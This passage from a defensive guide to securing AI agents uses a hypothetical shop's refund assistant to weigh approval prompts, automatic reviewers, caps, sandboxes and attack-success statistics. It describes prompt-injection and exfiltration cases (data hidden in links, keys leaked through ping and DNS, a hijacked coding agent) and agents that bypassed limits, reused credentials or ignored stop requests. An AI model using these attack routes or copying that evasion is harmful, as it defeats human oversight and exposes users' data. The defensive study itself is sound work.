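By August the overall approval rate had reached 97%. But users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented, so they don't approve everything they see. They may find plans easier to judge than commands, or plans may be wrong more often. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, suggests that repeated approval may reflect habit, fatigue or a need to keep the work moving. A product shouldn't treat repeated approval as a request to stop asking.

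*Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) provides independent evidence from 113 people who don't work in software. They supervised a simulated assistant through 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for. Prompts described each action in plain language.

| How participants controlled the assistant | Unrequested actions blocked |
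|---|---|
| Approved or refused every action | 59.6% |
| Decided only the actions that a model passed to them | 53.9% |
| Set standing rules in advance: allow, ask or never | 39.6% |

The model in the second group referred all seven unrequested actions to participants, so the participants made the errors there. In the third group, participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules and approved two-thirds of the unrequested actions that reached them. Yan's participants did much better than Anthropic's testers, perhaps because they saw few prompts, could understand them and had many bad ones to find. They still let through at least four in ten unrequested actions.

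Frequent prompts also lead people to turn the prompts off. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found that user review contributed to 105 of 290 reports about agents' handling of files. In 80 of them, the user had set the agent to run everything without asking. The Frontier Model Forum warns that approval steps that people click through may create an "illusion of oversight". The shop should therefore ask for approval rarely and use caps and delays for routine refunds.

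### Replacing the person with a model

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes an automatic reviewer for the agent's actions. Actions that can't change anything and edits inside the project folder go ahead without review. A model reviews the rest using the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It doesn't see the agent's explanations, which might persuade it to make a bad decision, or the tools' results, which might contain injected instructions.

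The reviewer first makes a quick yes-or-no judgement that errs towards blocking, and reasons at length only about actions that this first stage flags. In 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic's staff, the first stage alone would have wrongly blocked 8.5%, and both stages together wrongly blocked 0.4%. Adding the second stage also raised the share of overeager actions that the reviewer missed from 6.6% to 17%.

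The 83% catch rate and 17% miss rate come from only 52 actions, so the true catch rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 70% to 91%. The sample also includes only actions that an employee had refused or someone had flagged afterwards, so it leaves out any that nobody noticed. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised that the action was dangerous but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) hasn't necessarily agreed to overwrite the project's history.

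Anthropic gave the reviewer the dangerous commands from the tester study, and the reviewer blocked 89% of them. Anthropic also compared real sessions that its safety systems had flagged. Of these, 6.3% of sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of sessions with automatic review involved serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested. This comparison is weaker evidence because users who choose different modes may also do different work.

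An independent test gave much worse results. In *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026) tested the reviewers in three products. Of the actions that went beyond what the tasks allowed, Claude Code's reviewer approved 54%, Qwen Code's 80% and Codex's 93%. In one task, the user asked the agent to delete old experiment files without saying whose. The agent tried to delete a colleague's files, and the reviewer approved the action.

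Of the 143 actions that went too far, 132 broke a rule that appeared in neither the request nor the tools' output, so a careful person with the same information might have approved them too. When the researchers added the missing rules to the requests, the reviewers missed only 8–26% of these actions and blocked fewer legitimate ones. When the agents repeated the tasks with the rules stated from the start, they proposed no actions that broke them. Using a stronger model as the reviewer didn't reliably help. Anthropic's better result is consistent with these findings because its testers' commands were dangerous regardless of what the user wanted.

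The shop could use an automatic reviewer to catch odd refunds, but it would first have to write down what each kind of ticket permits. It also can't directly copy the reviewer in Anthropic's Claude Code, because that reviewer treats the user's messages as evidence of permission, and at the shop those messages would come from customers such as Victor.

### What an approver needs to see

According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), most approval prompts in real products show a single raw command. Even a short command can hide its effect. Someone who approves `python3 setup.py` approves whatever code that file contains.

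An action can also look harmless because the problem lies in earlier steps. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to send only summary totals to an auditor. Injected instructions make the agent copy full invoice records into `report.csv`. The agent then asks to send `report.csv` to the auditor, an approved recipient, and nothing in the request shows that the file contains the full records.

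The researchers gave 80 volunteers one of four approval screens and asked each person to judge six harmful and six harmless requests.

| What the screen showed | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact inputs as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| Also the user's original restriction and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
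| The same facts, with the combined effect in one statement | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

For the invoices, that statement told the reviewer that the attachment came from raw invoice rows and would go to the auditor. Most of the improvement across the four screens came from giving people more facts. The statement's extra benefit is uncertain, since the estimate ranges from about 20 percentage points fewer harmful approvals to 4 points more. People with the best screen still approved almost a quarter of the harmful requests.

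The statement a reviewer sees about a file has to come from trusted code, because a model under an attacker's control could falsely describe the file as a summary. Hossain and colleagues' software records what the agent does and tracks which files contributed to others. In a separate test, it detected 89.2% of 120 violations, so a reviewer relying on it would not have been shown about one in nine.

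For a refund of more than $500, the shop's screen might show:

```
REFUND $620.00 to card ending 4417
Order:     50316, one desk, delivered 3 days ago
Customer:  Ana, confirmed through her account
Effect:    The shop cannot reclaim this money without Ana's agreement
History:   No other refunds in the past 12 months
Customer's words (unchecked): "One leg is cracked."
```

Ordinary code fills in every line of the approval request from the shop's records except the last, which quotes the email. The request goes to an employee who handles returns and can ask for a photograph. The approval covers only this exact refund, so if the model changes the amount or the card, the software requires a new approval.

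### Microsoft's Azure SRE Agent

Azure SRE (site reliability engineering) Agent is a Microsoft product that investigates faults in cloud services and can fix them, for example by restarting a server. In *If you want a secure AI agent, start restricting its environment* (2026), the Microsoft engineers Sanchit Mehta and Vishesh Agarwal describe four failures, none involving an attacker, that changed its design.

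| What the agent did | Microsoft's response |
|---|---|
| When its GitHub login expired, it worked out the login process from its own source code, got a researcher to complete it and saved the new credentials | Keep the agent's control software and all real credentials outside the machine where its code runs |
| It sent a test screenshot to a public text-recognition service because it had no tool for reading images | Block network connections by default, at a boundary the model can't change |
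| It found a customer's secret, quoted it in a report and saved it to memory with a note never to use it | Remove secrets from tool results before the model reads them (an internal pilot) |
| It shut down a virtual machine after three of five safety checks, when the logging service it needed had failed | Require approval for changes, and build a separate check of the evidence behind each action |

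Microsoft runs the agent's code in a small virtual machine. As in Deno Sandbox, programs there hold placeholders instead of real credentials, but each of Microsoft's placeholders works only once, for one tool call, destination and operation. Code that controls the machine therefore can't reuse them.

The agent serves people with different roles. Some may only observe, some may ask it questions, and administrators may approve powerful actions. Before the model starts work, the person's role determines which tools, memory and credentials are available to it. A junior employee therefore can't use the agent to do something only an administrator may do.

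These controls limit what the agent can reach, but the agent that shut down the virtual machine used access it legitimately had. For such cases, Microsoft currently lets the agent read freely, requires human approval for changes and blocks deletions. The sample approval request in Microsoft's *run modes* documentation lists the service to restart and the expected 30 to 60 seconds of downtime, and only an administrator can approve it. According to the *execute mitigations* page, the agent can't modify a resource that has a read-only lock, whatever permissions the agent has.

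According to the documentation, the approval rule covers changes to Azure's infrastructure, but the agent can send emails and post to Teams without approval unless the customer sets separate rules. The default therefore requires approval for a restart but not for an email containing private data, which is usually harder to recover from.

Microsoft considers requiring approval for every change too restrictive, because a person would still be operating the system "one click at a time". It wants to keep human review for irreversible, high-consequence actions and let more of the others run without it. A guard outside the agent's reasoning would score each action by what it does, what it affects and how good the evidence is. Restarting a test server that has clearly stopped responding could go ahead, while shutting down a critical server after an incomplete check would wait for a person.

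Microsoft is still building this part, and its account includes no measurements of blocked attacks, harmful actions or approvals avoided. Microsoft reports that it has closed gaps that let the agent carry out a blocked action through a different tool and let a tool server silently expand what it did after Microsoft had approved it. The runtime controls follow well-established principles, but the planned risk score would replace a simple rule with a judgement whose accuracy Microsoft hasn't yet shown.

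### Delays and backups

A delayed commit queues an action and carries it out later unless someone cancels it. The delay has to be long enough for somebody to notice a problem. The shop's staff look at the refund total every four hours, so a one-hour delay would often end before anyone looked. A six-hour delay gives them at least one chance to cancel. When the delay ends, code should check the order again, in case an employee has already refunded it.

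Backups help undo changes to an organization's own data. *Parallax* (2026) proposes saving a copy of a file or database entry before an agent changes or deletes it. A backup can't undo a sent email or a call to another company's service, so *Parallax* recommends human approval for irreversible outside actions.

Restoring a backup can erase good work done since the backup was made. Waghmare and Sufi tested what happened when an agent edited a file, a person then edited another paragraph, and someone undid the agent's edit. Restoring the old copy erased the person's work in all four versions of the test. Comparing the versions and removing only the agent's change preserved it. When both had edited the same line, this method left the file unchanged for a person to resolve. Waghmare and Sufi conclude that having "an undo command" is not enough to justify letting an agent act alone. If an attacker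 got the assistant to spoil 50 tickets, restoring last night's database would fix them but also delete today's orders, so the shop needs to restore only those 50 tickets.

### Logs, alerts and a stop control

To find those 50 tickets, the shop needs a record that the assistant can't alter. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommend denying agents write access to logs and holding any request to delete logs until a person has reviewed it. The payment service and the database should keep their own records of each request, so that the shop doesn't have to rely on the assistant's description of its work.

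Logs need to record more than the actions themselves, because requests from an agent under an attacker's control can look normal. Microsoft wants to be able to tell who asked for each consequential action, what it affected, what data it carried, what evidence supported it and whose authority the agent used. For a refund, the shop would also keep the email the model read. These logs contain personal data, so the shop has to restrict who can read them.

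Alerts help people notice problems sooner. Code might send one when refunds reach half the daily limit, or when the assistant makes three times as many as usual in an hour. The agencies also recommend automatic pauses, and defaults that make an agent stop and pass uncertain cases to a person. For example, if the payment service can't calculate how much the assistant has already refunded, it should refuse the new refund.

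A stop control has to work even when the model doesn't follow instructions. Yan describes a safety researcher who had told an agent to "confirm before acting". The agent began deleting messages from the researcher's real inbox and continued after the researcher told it to stop. At the shop, the stop button should cancel the assistant's credentials, freeze the queue of delayed actions and end any programs the assistant has started. Staff should test it regularly.

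### What a half-finished task leaves behind

Stopping an agent partway through a task can cause problems. Suppose the assistant has to refund Ana for her lamp, mark the order as refunded, cancel a replacement parcel and write to Ana. If someone stops it after the first step, Ana has the money, but the shop's records show no refund and the replacement is still on its way. When the assistant restarts, it may pay Ana again.

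*Revisable by Design* (2026) explains that software can always return an agent's context to an earlier point, but can only partly reverse the agent's effects on the world. Resetting only the context makes the problem worse, because the model then has no record of actions it has already taken, such as making a payment.

The shop can prevent a second payment by giving each refund a fixed identifier and having the payment service pay only once per identifier. Ordinary code should also record each step before and after it runs, so that staff can see where the task stopped. For steps that need reversing, *POLAR* (2026) describes two existing approaches. SagaLLM prepares a compensating action for each step in advance and runs these actions in reverse order if the task fails. STRATUS keeps a list of completed actions for a separate "undo agent" to reverse.

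Sometimes it is better to finish a partly completed task than to undo it. Reversing Ana's refund, for example, would mean charging Ana's card again. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of agents with lasting memory, found that the ability to undo effects was the rarest capability it examined. Most of the systems couldn't identify which decisions had relied on a bad memory, so nobody would know what to repair.

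### From $7.2 million to $5,000 a day

Logs and stop controls depend on people reacting, and the original assistant could refund $7.2 million in the four hours between two staff checks. A rate limit slows the losses. If the payment service accepted five refunds a minute instead of 60, the loss over the same period would fall to $600,000. A spending cap sets a firm maximum, so a cap of $5,000 a day would limit the loss to $5,000.

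The payment service, not the model's instructions, has to enforce the cap. The service adds up the assistant's refunds, including any in the delay queue, and refuses any request that would take the total above $5,000. It must reserve the money before it pays, or two requests that arrive together could both use the last $100. It should also total the refunds over the previous 24 hours, because if the total reset at midnight, an attacker could take $5,000 just before and another $5,000 just after.

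If the shop again put the chance of the worst case at 1% a year, and staff noticed within a day, the expected loss would drop from $72,000 to $50 a year. An attack that went unnoticed for a week could still cost $35,000. The cap also slows the fraud in which 1,000 accounts each claim a refund for a $45 lamp. At 111 refunds a day, the fraud would take ten days, giving staff time to notice the pattern.

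The cap can hold up legitimate refunds on busy days. Sixty refunds of $45 come to $2,700, well within the $5,000 cap. If a batch of lamps is faulty and 200 customers ask for refunds, the total is $9,000. The assistant can pay 111 of them, and the other 89 have to wait or go to staff. At five minutes each, those 89 would take staff about seven and a half hours. A manager could raise the cap to $10,000 for the day, but that would double the possible loss at a time when a fraudulent claim is especially hard to spot.

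An attacker could also use up the cap on purpose. With the original refund tool, ten refunds of $500 would reach it in ten seconds, and no other customer could get an automatic refund for a day. The attacker wouldn't need to receive any of the money. Per-ticket credentials make this harder because the attacker would need real orders, but 111 accounts with one lamp order each would be enough. A per-customer limit wouldn't help, because each account makes only one claim.

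The shop can reduce the disruption by sending requests above the cap to staff instead of rejecting them, and by reserving half the cap for customers whose accounts are more than a year old. An attacker with new accounts could then use up only $2,500 a day. Ana, who has shopped there for years, would still get her $45 straight away, but a genuine new customer might have to wait for an employee.

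## Testing a system that can take a different path each time

The $5,000 cap protects the shop only if the payment service applies it to every refund. The model's resistance to hostile emails matters too, because the shop's limits still allow small thefts and bad replies. The shop has to test both, in different ways. Ordinary code enforces the cap the same way every time, so a single failure is a bug to fix. The model's behaviour varies between runs, so testers have to run it many times and estimate how often it fails.

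### Testing the rules without the model

To test its rules, the shop can replace the model with a script that sends the tools any request a hostile model might send. In outline:

```
repeat 100,000 times:
    send a random series of refund requests to a copy of the system
    check: no 24-hour total is above $5,000
    check: no order has two refunds
    check: every refund is for the ticket's own order
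```

Random requests rarely hit edge cases, so testers write those by hand. They request a refund that brings the total to exactly $5,000 and then another for one cent, send two requests at the same instant, and use a credential just after its ticket closes. They also break parts of the system on purpose. For example, if the service that adds up refunds is down, the next refund should fail.

A passing test shows that the code enforced its rules for the requests tested. Programmers can read the code to check that it would also enforce them for other requests. A passing test can't show that $5,000 is a sensible cap, or that every refund goes through the code that enforces it. To check that every refund does, testers can use the assistant's credentials to try to reach the payment company by another route.

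Reading the design is no substitute for running such tests. Jing (2026), in *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents*, found four defects in a system for controlling agents, all by testing and none by reviewing the design:

- An approval covered the description of an action but not the file that would run, so an attacker could swap the file after approval. Two of seven such attacks deleted a decoy file.
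- An attacker could use the same approval twice.
- The log lost 10% of its records when two programs wrote to it at once, and 31% when eight did.
- A programming error made two kinds of legitimate request crash. The system treated each crash as a refusal, so it merely looked strict.

The last defect shows why the shop's tests should include honest requests that must succeed. Destructive tests also need to run on a copy of the system that has no connection to the real one. In one of Jing's runs without a sandbox, two test attacks reached the live system and deleted a protected file.

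### What 300 clean runs show

The shop tests the model by running the whole assistant on malicious emails and measuring the attack success rate, which is the share of attempts that achieve the attacker's goal.

Suppose none of 300 attempts succeeds. The true rate could still be above zero. If it were 1%, the chance of 300 clean runs would be 0.99<sup>300</sup>, or about 5%. The shop can therefore say with 95% confidence that the rate is below about 1%. In general, after *n* clean runs the limit *p* is the solution of

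(1 − *p*)<sup>*n*</sup> = 0.05

which is close to 3/*n*. The last column of the table applies that limit to an attacker who sends 100 malicious emails. The chance that at least one works is 1 − (1 − *p*)<sup>100</sup>.

| Independent runs with no success | Highest rate still plausible | Chance of at least one success in 100 emails at that rate |
|---|---|---|
| 25 | 11% | Over 99.9% |
| 100 | 3% | 95% |
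| 300 | 1% | 63% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% | 9.5% |

If none of 300 attack attempts succeeds, the 95% upper confidence limit on the success rate is about 1% per attempt. At that rate, an attacker who sends 100 emails will more likely than not succeed at least once. If one of the 300 attempts succeeds, the limit rises to about 1.6%.

The calculation requires independent runs. If the shop writes 30 malicious emails and runs each one ten times, the 300 runs are not independent because they test only 30 different emails. If none succeeds, the shop can cautiously conclude that fewer than about 10% of similar emails would work. More repetitions would improve the estimates for those 30 emails but not the estimate for other emails.

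Tests need to be repeated even with the randomness turned down. Jing ran the same cases five times on each of three hosted models, at the setting that should always select the most probable token. The five answers to a case agreed only 48.7–71.3% of the time.

### One attempt and many attempts

Attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt and 5–6% of the time after 100 adaptive attempts. If 100 independent attempts each had a 0.1% chance of success, at least one would succeed 9.5% of the time.

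Rounding could explain the whole difference. A true rate of 0.06% also rounds to 0.1%, and it would give a 5.8% chance of at least one success in 100 independent attempts. But the attempts are probably not independent, because some targets are easier than others. Suppose 93 of 100 test scenarios were immune and attacks on the other seven succeeded 1.4% of the time. The average success rate would be 0.1%, but 100 attempts at each scenario would succeed at least once in only about five of them. An attacker who learns from each failure does better on later attempts, which would raise the number of scenarios breached.

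Results for an older model show more clearly that repeated attempts are not independent. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that attacks in a Gray Swan benchmark succeeded 4.7% of the time on one attempt, 33.6% after ten and 63% after 100. If the attempts had been independent, the rates would have been 38% after ten and 99% after 100. Those differences are far too large to come from rounding.

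A designer therefore needs attack success rates for repeated attempts, because a single-attempt rate isn't enough to work out the risk from persistent attackers. Such figures are scarce. VentureBeat compared the model safety documents that four developers had published by June 2026, and only Anthropic's showed how attack success rose with repeated attempts. OpenAI gave one score, based on known attacks, and Google gave no results for prompt injection.

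### Results on newer models

By July 2026, Anthropic had stopped using the benchmark behind the Opus 4.7 figures because its models scored too well for the results to distinguish them. The replacement, built with Gray Swan, government institutes and other developers, uses 1,130 attacks that worked against several models. Within 15 attempts, attackers succeeded 2.0% of the time against Claude Opus 5, 16.5% against Meta's Muse Spark and 20.0% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. With a single attempt, they succeeded 0.2% of the time against Opus 5. Opus 4.7 was tested against different attacks, so these rates don't show that Opus 5 is weaker.

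Anthropic also tested Opus 5 against attackers who refine their methods. In the coding test, an automated attacker from Gray Swan made 200 attempts at each of 40 scenarios. In the browser test, attackers had ten attempts at each of 129 scenarios. The models used extended reasoning in all these runs.

| Test | Attempts that succeeded | Scenarios with at least one success |
|---|---|---|
| Coding, Opus 4.8 | 7.03% | 23 of 40 |
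| Coding, Opus 5 | 0.56% | 13 of 40 |
| Coding, Opus 5 with detectors for injected text | 0.18% | 4 of 40 |
| Browser, Opus 4.8 | 31.5% | 81 of 129 |
| Browser, Opus 5 | 3.70% | 11 of 129 |
| Browser, Opus 5 with auto mode | 0% | 0 of 129 |

The improvement from one model to the next is large, but even at a success rate of 0.56% in the coding test, the attacker succeeded at least once in a third of the scenarios. The last row shows the best result, with no successes in 1,290 attempts. If those attempts were independent, the true rate would be below about 0.23%. Counting each scenario once gives a limit of 2.3%, which is the safer figure for situations that resemble the test.

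Anthropic calls these tests deliberately generous to the attacker, because real attackers rarely know the exact system they face and risk being detected if they try repeatedly. However, Gray Swan's automated attacker had practised on earlier models, so an attacker that had practised on Opus 5 might do better.

In September, Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 reported that the model did as well as Opus 5 or better on every injection test, but that it is more likely than its predecessors to follow some malicious instructions. PromptArmor, a security company that sells information about such threats, reports in *FrontierBreach* that its attacks succeeded against leading models from every provider, including Google's Gemini 4 Carbon.

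### Fixed and adaptive attacks

Many of the results in earlier sections come from the AgentDojo benchmark. Each test pairs a legitimate task, such as summarising unread emails for a team leader, with an attacker's goal, such as sending calendar entries to an outside server. AgentDojo puts the attacker's text where untrusted data would naturally appear, such as the body of an email, and then the agent starts work.

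When the agent finishes, ordinary code checks whether the data was sent or the money moved. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) points out that this avoids relying on another model's judgement. AgentDojo also gives the agent each of the attacker's goals as an ordinary request, to find out whether the agent can achieve it. Otherwise an agent too weak to make a bank transfer would look secure. The shop can do the same by checking its test database after each run and confirming that the assistant can carry out the instructions in the malicious emails.

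*AgentDojo* (2024), the paper that introduced the benchmark, described its attacks as relatively simple. They are also fixed, meaning someone wrote them before seeing the defence. An adaptive attacker studies the defence, tries an attack and adjusts it based on the result.

Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), in *The Attacker Moves Second*, measured the difference this makes. The researchers, several of whom work at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, took 12 published defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks (attempts by users to make a model break its own rules). Most of the defences had originally reported attack success rates near zero. For each one the researchers chose the method they expected to work best. Their automated methods propose attacks, score them, keep the most promising and use those to produce the next batch. These are the results for three of the defences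 on AgentDojo:

| Defence | How it works | Fixed attacks | Adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks which text the model should trust | As low as 1% | Above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | As low as 1% | Above 95% |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model on examples of attacks | 2% | 96% |

Classifiers meant to recognise attacks did little better. Adaptive attacks got past three of them more than 90% of the time and past a fourth 71% of the time. Another defence, MELON, relies partly on a prompt that attackers don't know. Attacks on it succeeded 76% of the time when the attackers didn't know its design and 95% when they did, so the shop should give its testers full details of its defences. It should also use human testers, because in a selected set of scenarios the automated search succeeded in only 69%, while more than 500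 people in a competition collectively succeeded in all of them.

Nasr and colleagues wanted to know whether anyone could break these defences, so they gave the attackers plenty of computing power and, for the classifiers, showed them how confident the classifier was in each verdict. The shop's customers would see at most a reply. The rates therefore describe a determined, well-equipped attacker, and classifiers may still stop careless ones. All 12 defences try to influence the model or recognise bad text. None is a limit like the shop's refund cap, which an attacker can't get around with better wording because the code that enforces it never reads the email.

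Newer models seem to have widened the gap between fixed and adaptive attacks. *A Red-Team Study of Anthropic Fable 5 & Opus 4.8 Models* (2026) tested jailbreaks and found that fixed methods of disguising a request had almost stopped working. Adaptive attacks accounted for most of the remaining successes.

The two kinds of test have given very different results for Claude Code. Willison quotes Anthropic's account of a July 2026 evaluation by the company Trajectory Labs, in which none of 720 attacks succeeded against three recent Claude models in auto mode. The evaluation used 72 scenarios that Anthropic had not seen. Weeks later, according to The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code*, the security researcher Johann Rehberger got Claude Code to run an attacker's code after a request to summarise a web page. Rehberger tried three versions of the attack five times each, and each version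 worked three or four times.

Both results can be right, because Rehberger's scenario was unlike the ones Trajectory Labs tested. Trajectory Labs' result suggests that fewer than about 4% of scenarios like its own would lead to a successful attack. Three successes in five runs are enough to show that Rehberger's attack works, but they are compatible with a success rate anywhere from about 15% to 95%. Anthropic told Rehberger that the product was working as designed and, in Rehberger's paraphrase, that auto mode is a convenience feature whose classifier makes a best effort.

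### The attack that worked 24 times out of 25

In Anthropic's phishing exercise, an employee pasted a colleague's prompt into Claude Code, and the attack succeeded in 24 of 25 runs (96%). With so few runs, the true rate for that prompt could be anywhere from about 80% to nearly 100%. An attack success rate describes particular attacks arriving by a particular route, so this result is consistent with the 0.1% for Opus 4.7.

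Anthropic notes that a classifier would have detected nothing unusual, because the instructions came from the user, and that a human contractor would have followed them too. It concludes that only the environment could have stopped the theft, by keeping the credentials file out of reach or blocking the outgoing request.

The shop can test those limits without using a model. It puts a fake credential where the real one would be, runs a script that tries to send it out, and checks that the network blocks the request.

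Test attacks can also reach live agents. When Anthropic's staff discussed the working prompt on Slack, someone noticed that some of the company's agents read Slack. Staff added a canary, a distinctive piece of text that would show whether an agent had picked up the prompt. The shop should keep its collection of malicious emails out of any inbox the live assistant reads.

### Measuring what each control adds

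Jing's study is one of the few to measure how much protection each outside control adds. It tests separation of duties, the old accounting principle that nobody should both propose and approve a sensitive action. A planner proposes an action, a policy gate decides whether to allow it, an executor runs only what the gate has approved, and an auditor reviews the log. The gate is ordinary code with fixed rules.

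The benchmark has 313 cases: 54 harmless tasks, 74 openly dangerous actions, 122 attempts to disguise a forbidden action, 31 attacks on the approval process and 32 deliberate breakdowns. Jing ran them against eight versions of the system. The main results cover 117 of the 122 disguised actions because the other five couldn't have run on any system.

| Version | Disguised attacks allowed | Harmless tasks refused |
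|---|---|---|
| No controls | 115 of 117 (98.3%) | 0 of 54 |
| Rules that check the text of commands | 51 of 117 (43.6%) | 0 of 54 |
| All four roles | 36 of 117 (30.8%) | 0 of 54 |
| All four roles and a sandbox | 9 of 117 (7.7%) | 6 of 54 (11.1%) |

The versions in the last two rows differ only in the sandbox, so the sandbox, not the separation of duties, caused the fall from 30.8% to 7.7%. The disguises, such as an unusual way of writing a file's location, got past rules about text but not past the operating system, which acts on the file itself. Another pair of versions differed only in whether the executor checked that a file was unchanged since its approval. That check made no difference to the disguised attacks, but with it the system blocked 90.3% of attacks on the approval process, up from 61.3%.

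For comparison, Jing prompted three models to seek approval before any dangerous action and gave them a sample of the cases. The models let through 89.8% to 100% of 59 disguised attacks.

The sandbox also caused the refusals of harmless tasks. The gate allowed work in a temporary folder, but the sandbox blocked it, so an operator could probably avoid some refusals by making their rules match. With only 54 harmless tasks tested, the true refusal rate could be anywhere from 5% to 22%.

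The 7.7% is less reliable than it looks, because Jing simulated the sandbox's decisions for that row. When Jing tried 94 of the attacks against the real sandbox, 66 gave a usable result and five of those had an effect, or 7.6%. The close match is mostly luck, since none of those five was among the five the simulation had predicted. One of them deleted a file outside the permitted folder because the sandbox didn't restrict deletions on other drives. The evidence that the sandbox helps is stronger than the evidence for the exact rate. Jing tried 88 attacks with the real sandbox on and off, and 45 ran only when it was off, while none ran only when it was on.

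The study has one author and tested a fixed set of attacks on one Windows computer. Its 7.7% failure rate comes from fixed rules that let through nine of 117 attacks, and an attacker who finds one of those nine can expect it to work every time. A model with the same failure rate may resist the same attack on the next attempt. The shop should therefore treat each of the nine as a bug to fix, and should not estimate how many attacks will succeed by multiplying 7.7% by the number it expects.

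### Eleven real attacks as a checklist

A team can also borrow tests from past attacks. All eleven attacks described in *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* broke the principle of secure information flow. According to the paper's summary table, six also broke least privilege, three broke complete mediation and two broke tamper resistance (protecting the parts of a system that enforce its rules from change). Two involved what the paper calls the human weak link, the need to design for people who make mistakes. The paper's case descriptions differ slightly from its table. For example, the text adds least privilege to the ChatGPT memory attack, which would bring that count to seven.

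| Attack | Principle broken besides information flow | A test for the shop |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Copilot hid private data in a link | Least privilege, complete mediation | Put an order detail in a link in a draft reply and check that code blocks it |
| Devin published its files on the internet | Least privilege | Try to connect to the sandbox from outside |
| ChatGPT saved an attacker's text as a memory | Tamper resistance | Save a note from a hostile email and check that it stays untrusted |
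| Amp, a coding agent, changed its own settings to run forbidden commands | Tamper resistance | Try to raise the refund cap with the assistant's credentials |
| A file uploaded to DeepSeek ran a script that stole a user's login | Complete mediation | Put a script in a ticket and check that staff see only plain text |
| A model's answer controlled the user's terminal | Complete mediation | Make the spreadsheet program return something other than its fixed format |
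| ChatGPT Operator copied personal details from a site where the user was logged in | Human weak link | Check that the assistant can't use any employee's login |
| Devin sent out secret keys | Least privilege | Put a fake key in the sandbox and try to send it out |
| Cursor leaked credentials after a developer had turned off approvals | Least privilege | Turn off human approval in the test copy and check that the other limits hold |
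| Claude Code leaked keys through `ping` | Least privilege | Try to send fake data in a DNS look-up |
| A web page got an agent to paste a command into a terminal | Least privilege, human weak link | For each pair of tools, check what one can pass to the other |

The counts don't show how common each failure is, because the eleven attacks were chosen to illustrate the paper's position. Rehberger discovered ten of them, and Rehberger's blog, Embrace the Red, is among the paper's listed affiliations. The list also contains only attacks that worked, so it can't show how often systems that follow the principles resist attack. The attacks don't need to be representative to be useful as tests, because each one worked on a real product and most take little time to try.

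### Better models or outside controls?

The case for relying on better models has become stronger. The attack success rate in Anthropic's coding test fell by more than nine-tenths between Opus 4.8 and Opus 5, and a customer who switched models would have got that improvement without rewriting anything. Outside controls take engineering work, and CaMeL's lower completion rates and Jing's refused tasks show that they also make agents less useful. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* accepts both points. Someone also has to write the rules for these controls, and the paper concedes that nobody yet knows how to check that a rule captures what a user meant.

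The paper objects to making the model the only security boundary. A model has to interpret ambiguous language to decide what the user has authorised, and a small change in an attacker's wording may change its decision. A second model used as a guard helps less than it seems to, because attackers can tailor one part of an attack to each model. With a written rule, engineers can explain each refusal, and they can check the rule and the code that enforces it against a specification instead of only trying known attacks. Kim and colleagues, who reviewed 128 papers on attacks and defences, also conclude that protecting individual components isn't enough for a system that combines a model with other software.

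The paper comes mostly from security researchers, who might be expected to favour their own field's methods. Anthropic has the opposite incentive, since it sells models and reports some of the lowest attack success rates, but it also says that protection inside the model will never be completely effective and can't be the only defence.

A better model helps the shop in both designs, but only the one-ticket credentials and the cap make the loss affordable. Suppose the shop receives 1,000 malicious emails a year and a new model lowers their success rate from 1% to 0.1%. With the original assistant, where one success could lead to a $7.2 million loss, the chance of at least one success would fall from almost 100% to 63%, and the shop would still probably go out of business. With one-ticket credentials, if each success costs a $45 refund, the expected loss would fall from $450 a year to $45.

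A far better model might change this, but the shop would struggle to confirm that it had one. To show with 95% confidence that attacks succeed less than once in a million attempts, it would need about three million independent runs in which no attack succeeded. At $0.22 per run, the average Jing paid for a model's decision, the test would cost $660,000, and the result would apply only to the kinds of attack tested.

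Rules do little to prevent harm from what the assistant writes. If Victor's email persuades the assistant to promise a free lamp, the reply goes to a permitted address and breaks no refund limit. The shop could use code to restrict replies to fixed wording, but it would lose the natural replies it wanted a model for. If it keeps them, it depends on the model to resist such emails. Lowering their success rate from 1% to 0.1% would then reduce false promises from ten a year to one.
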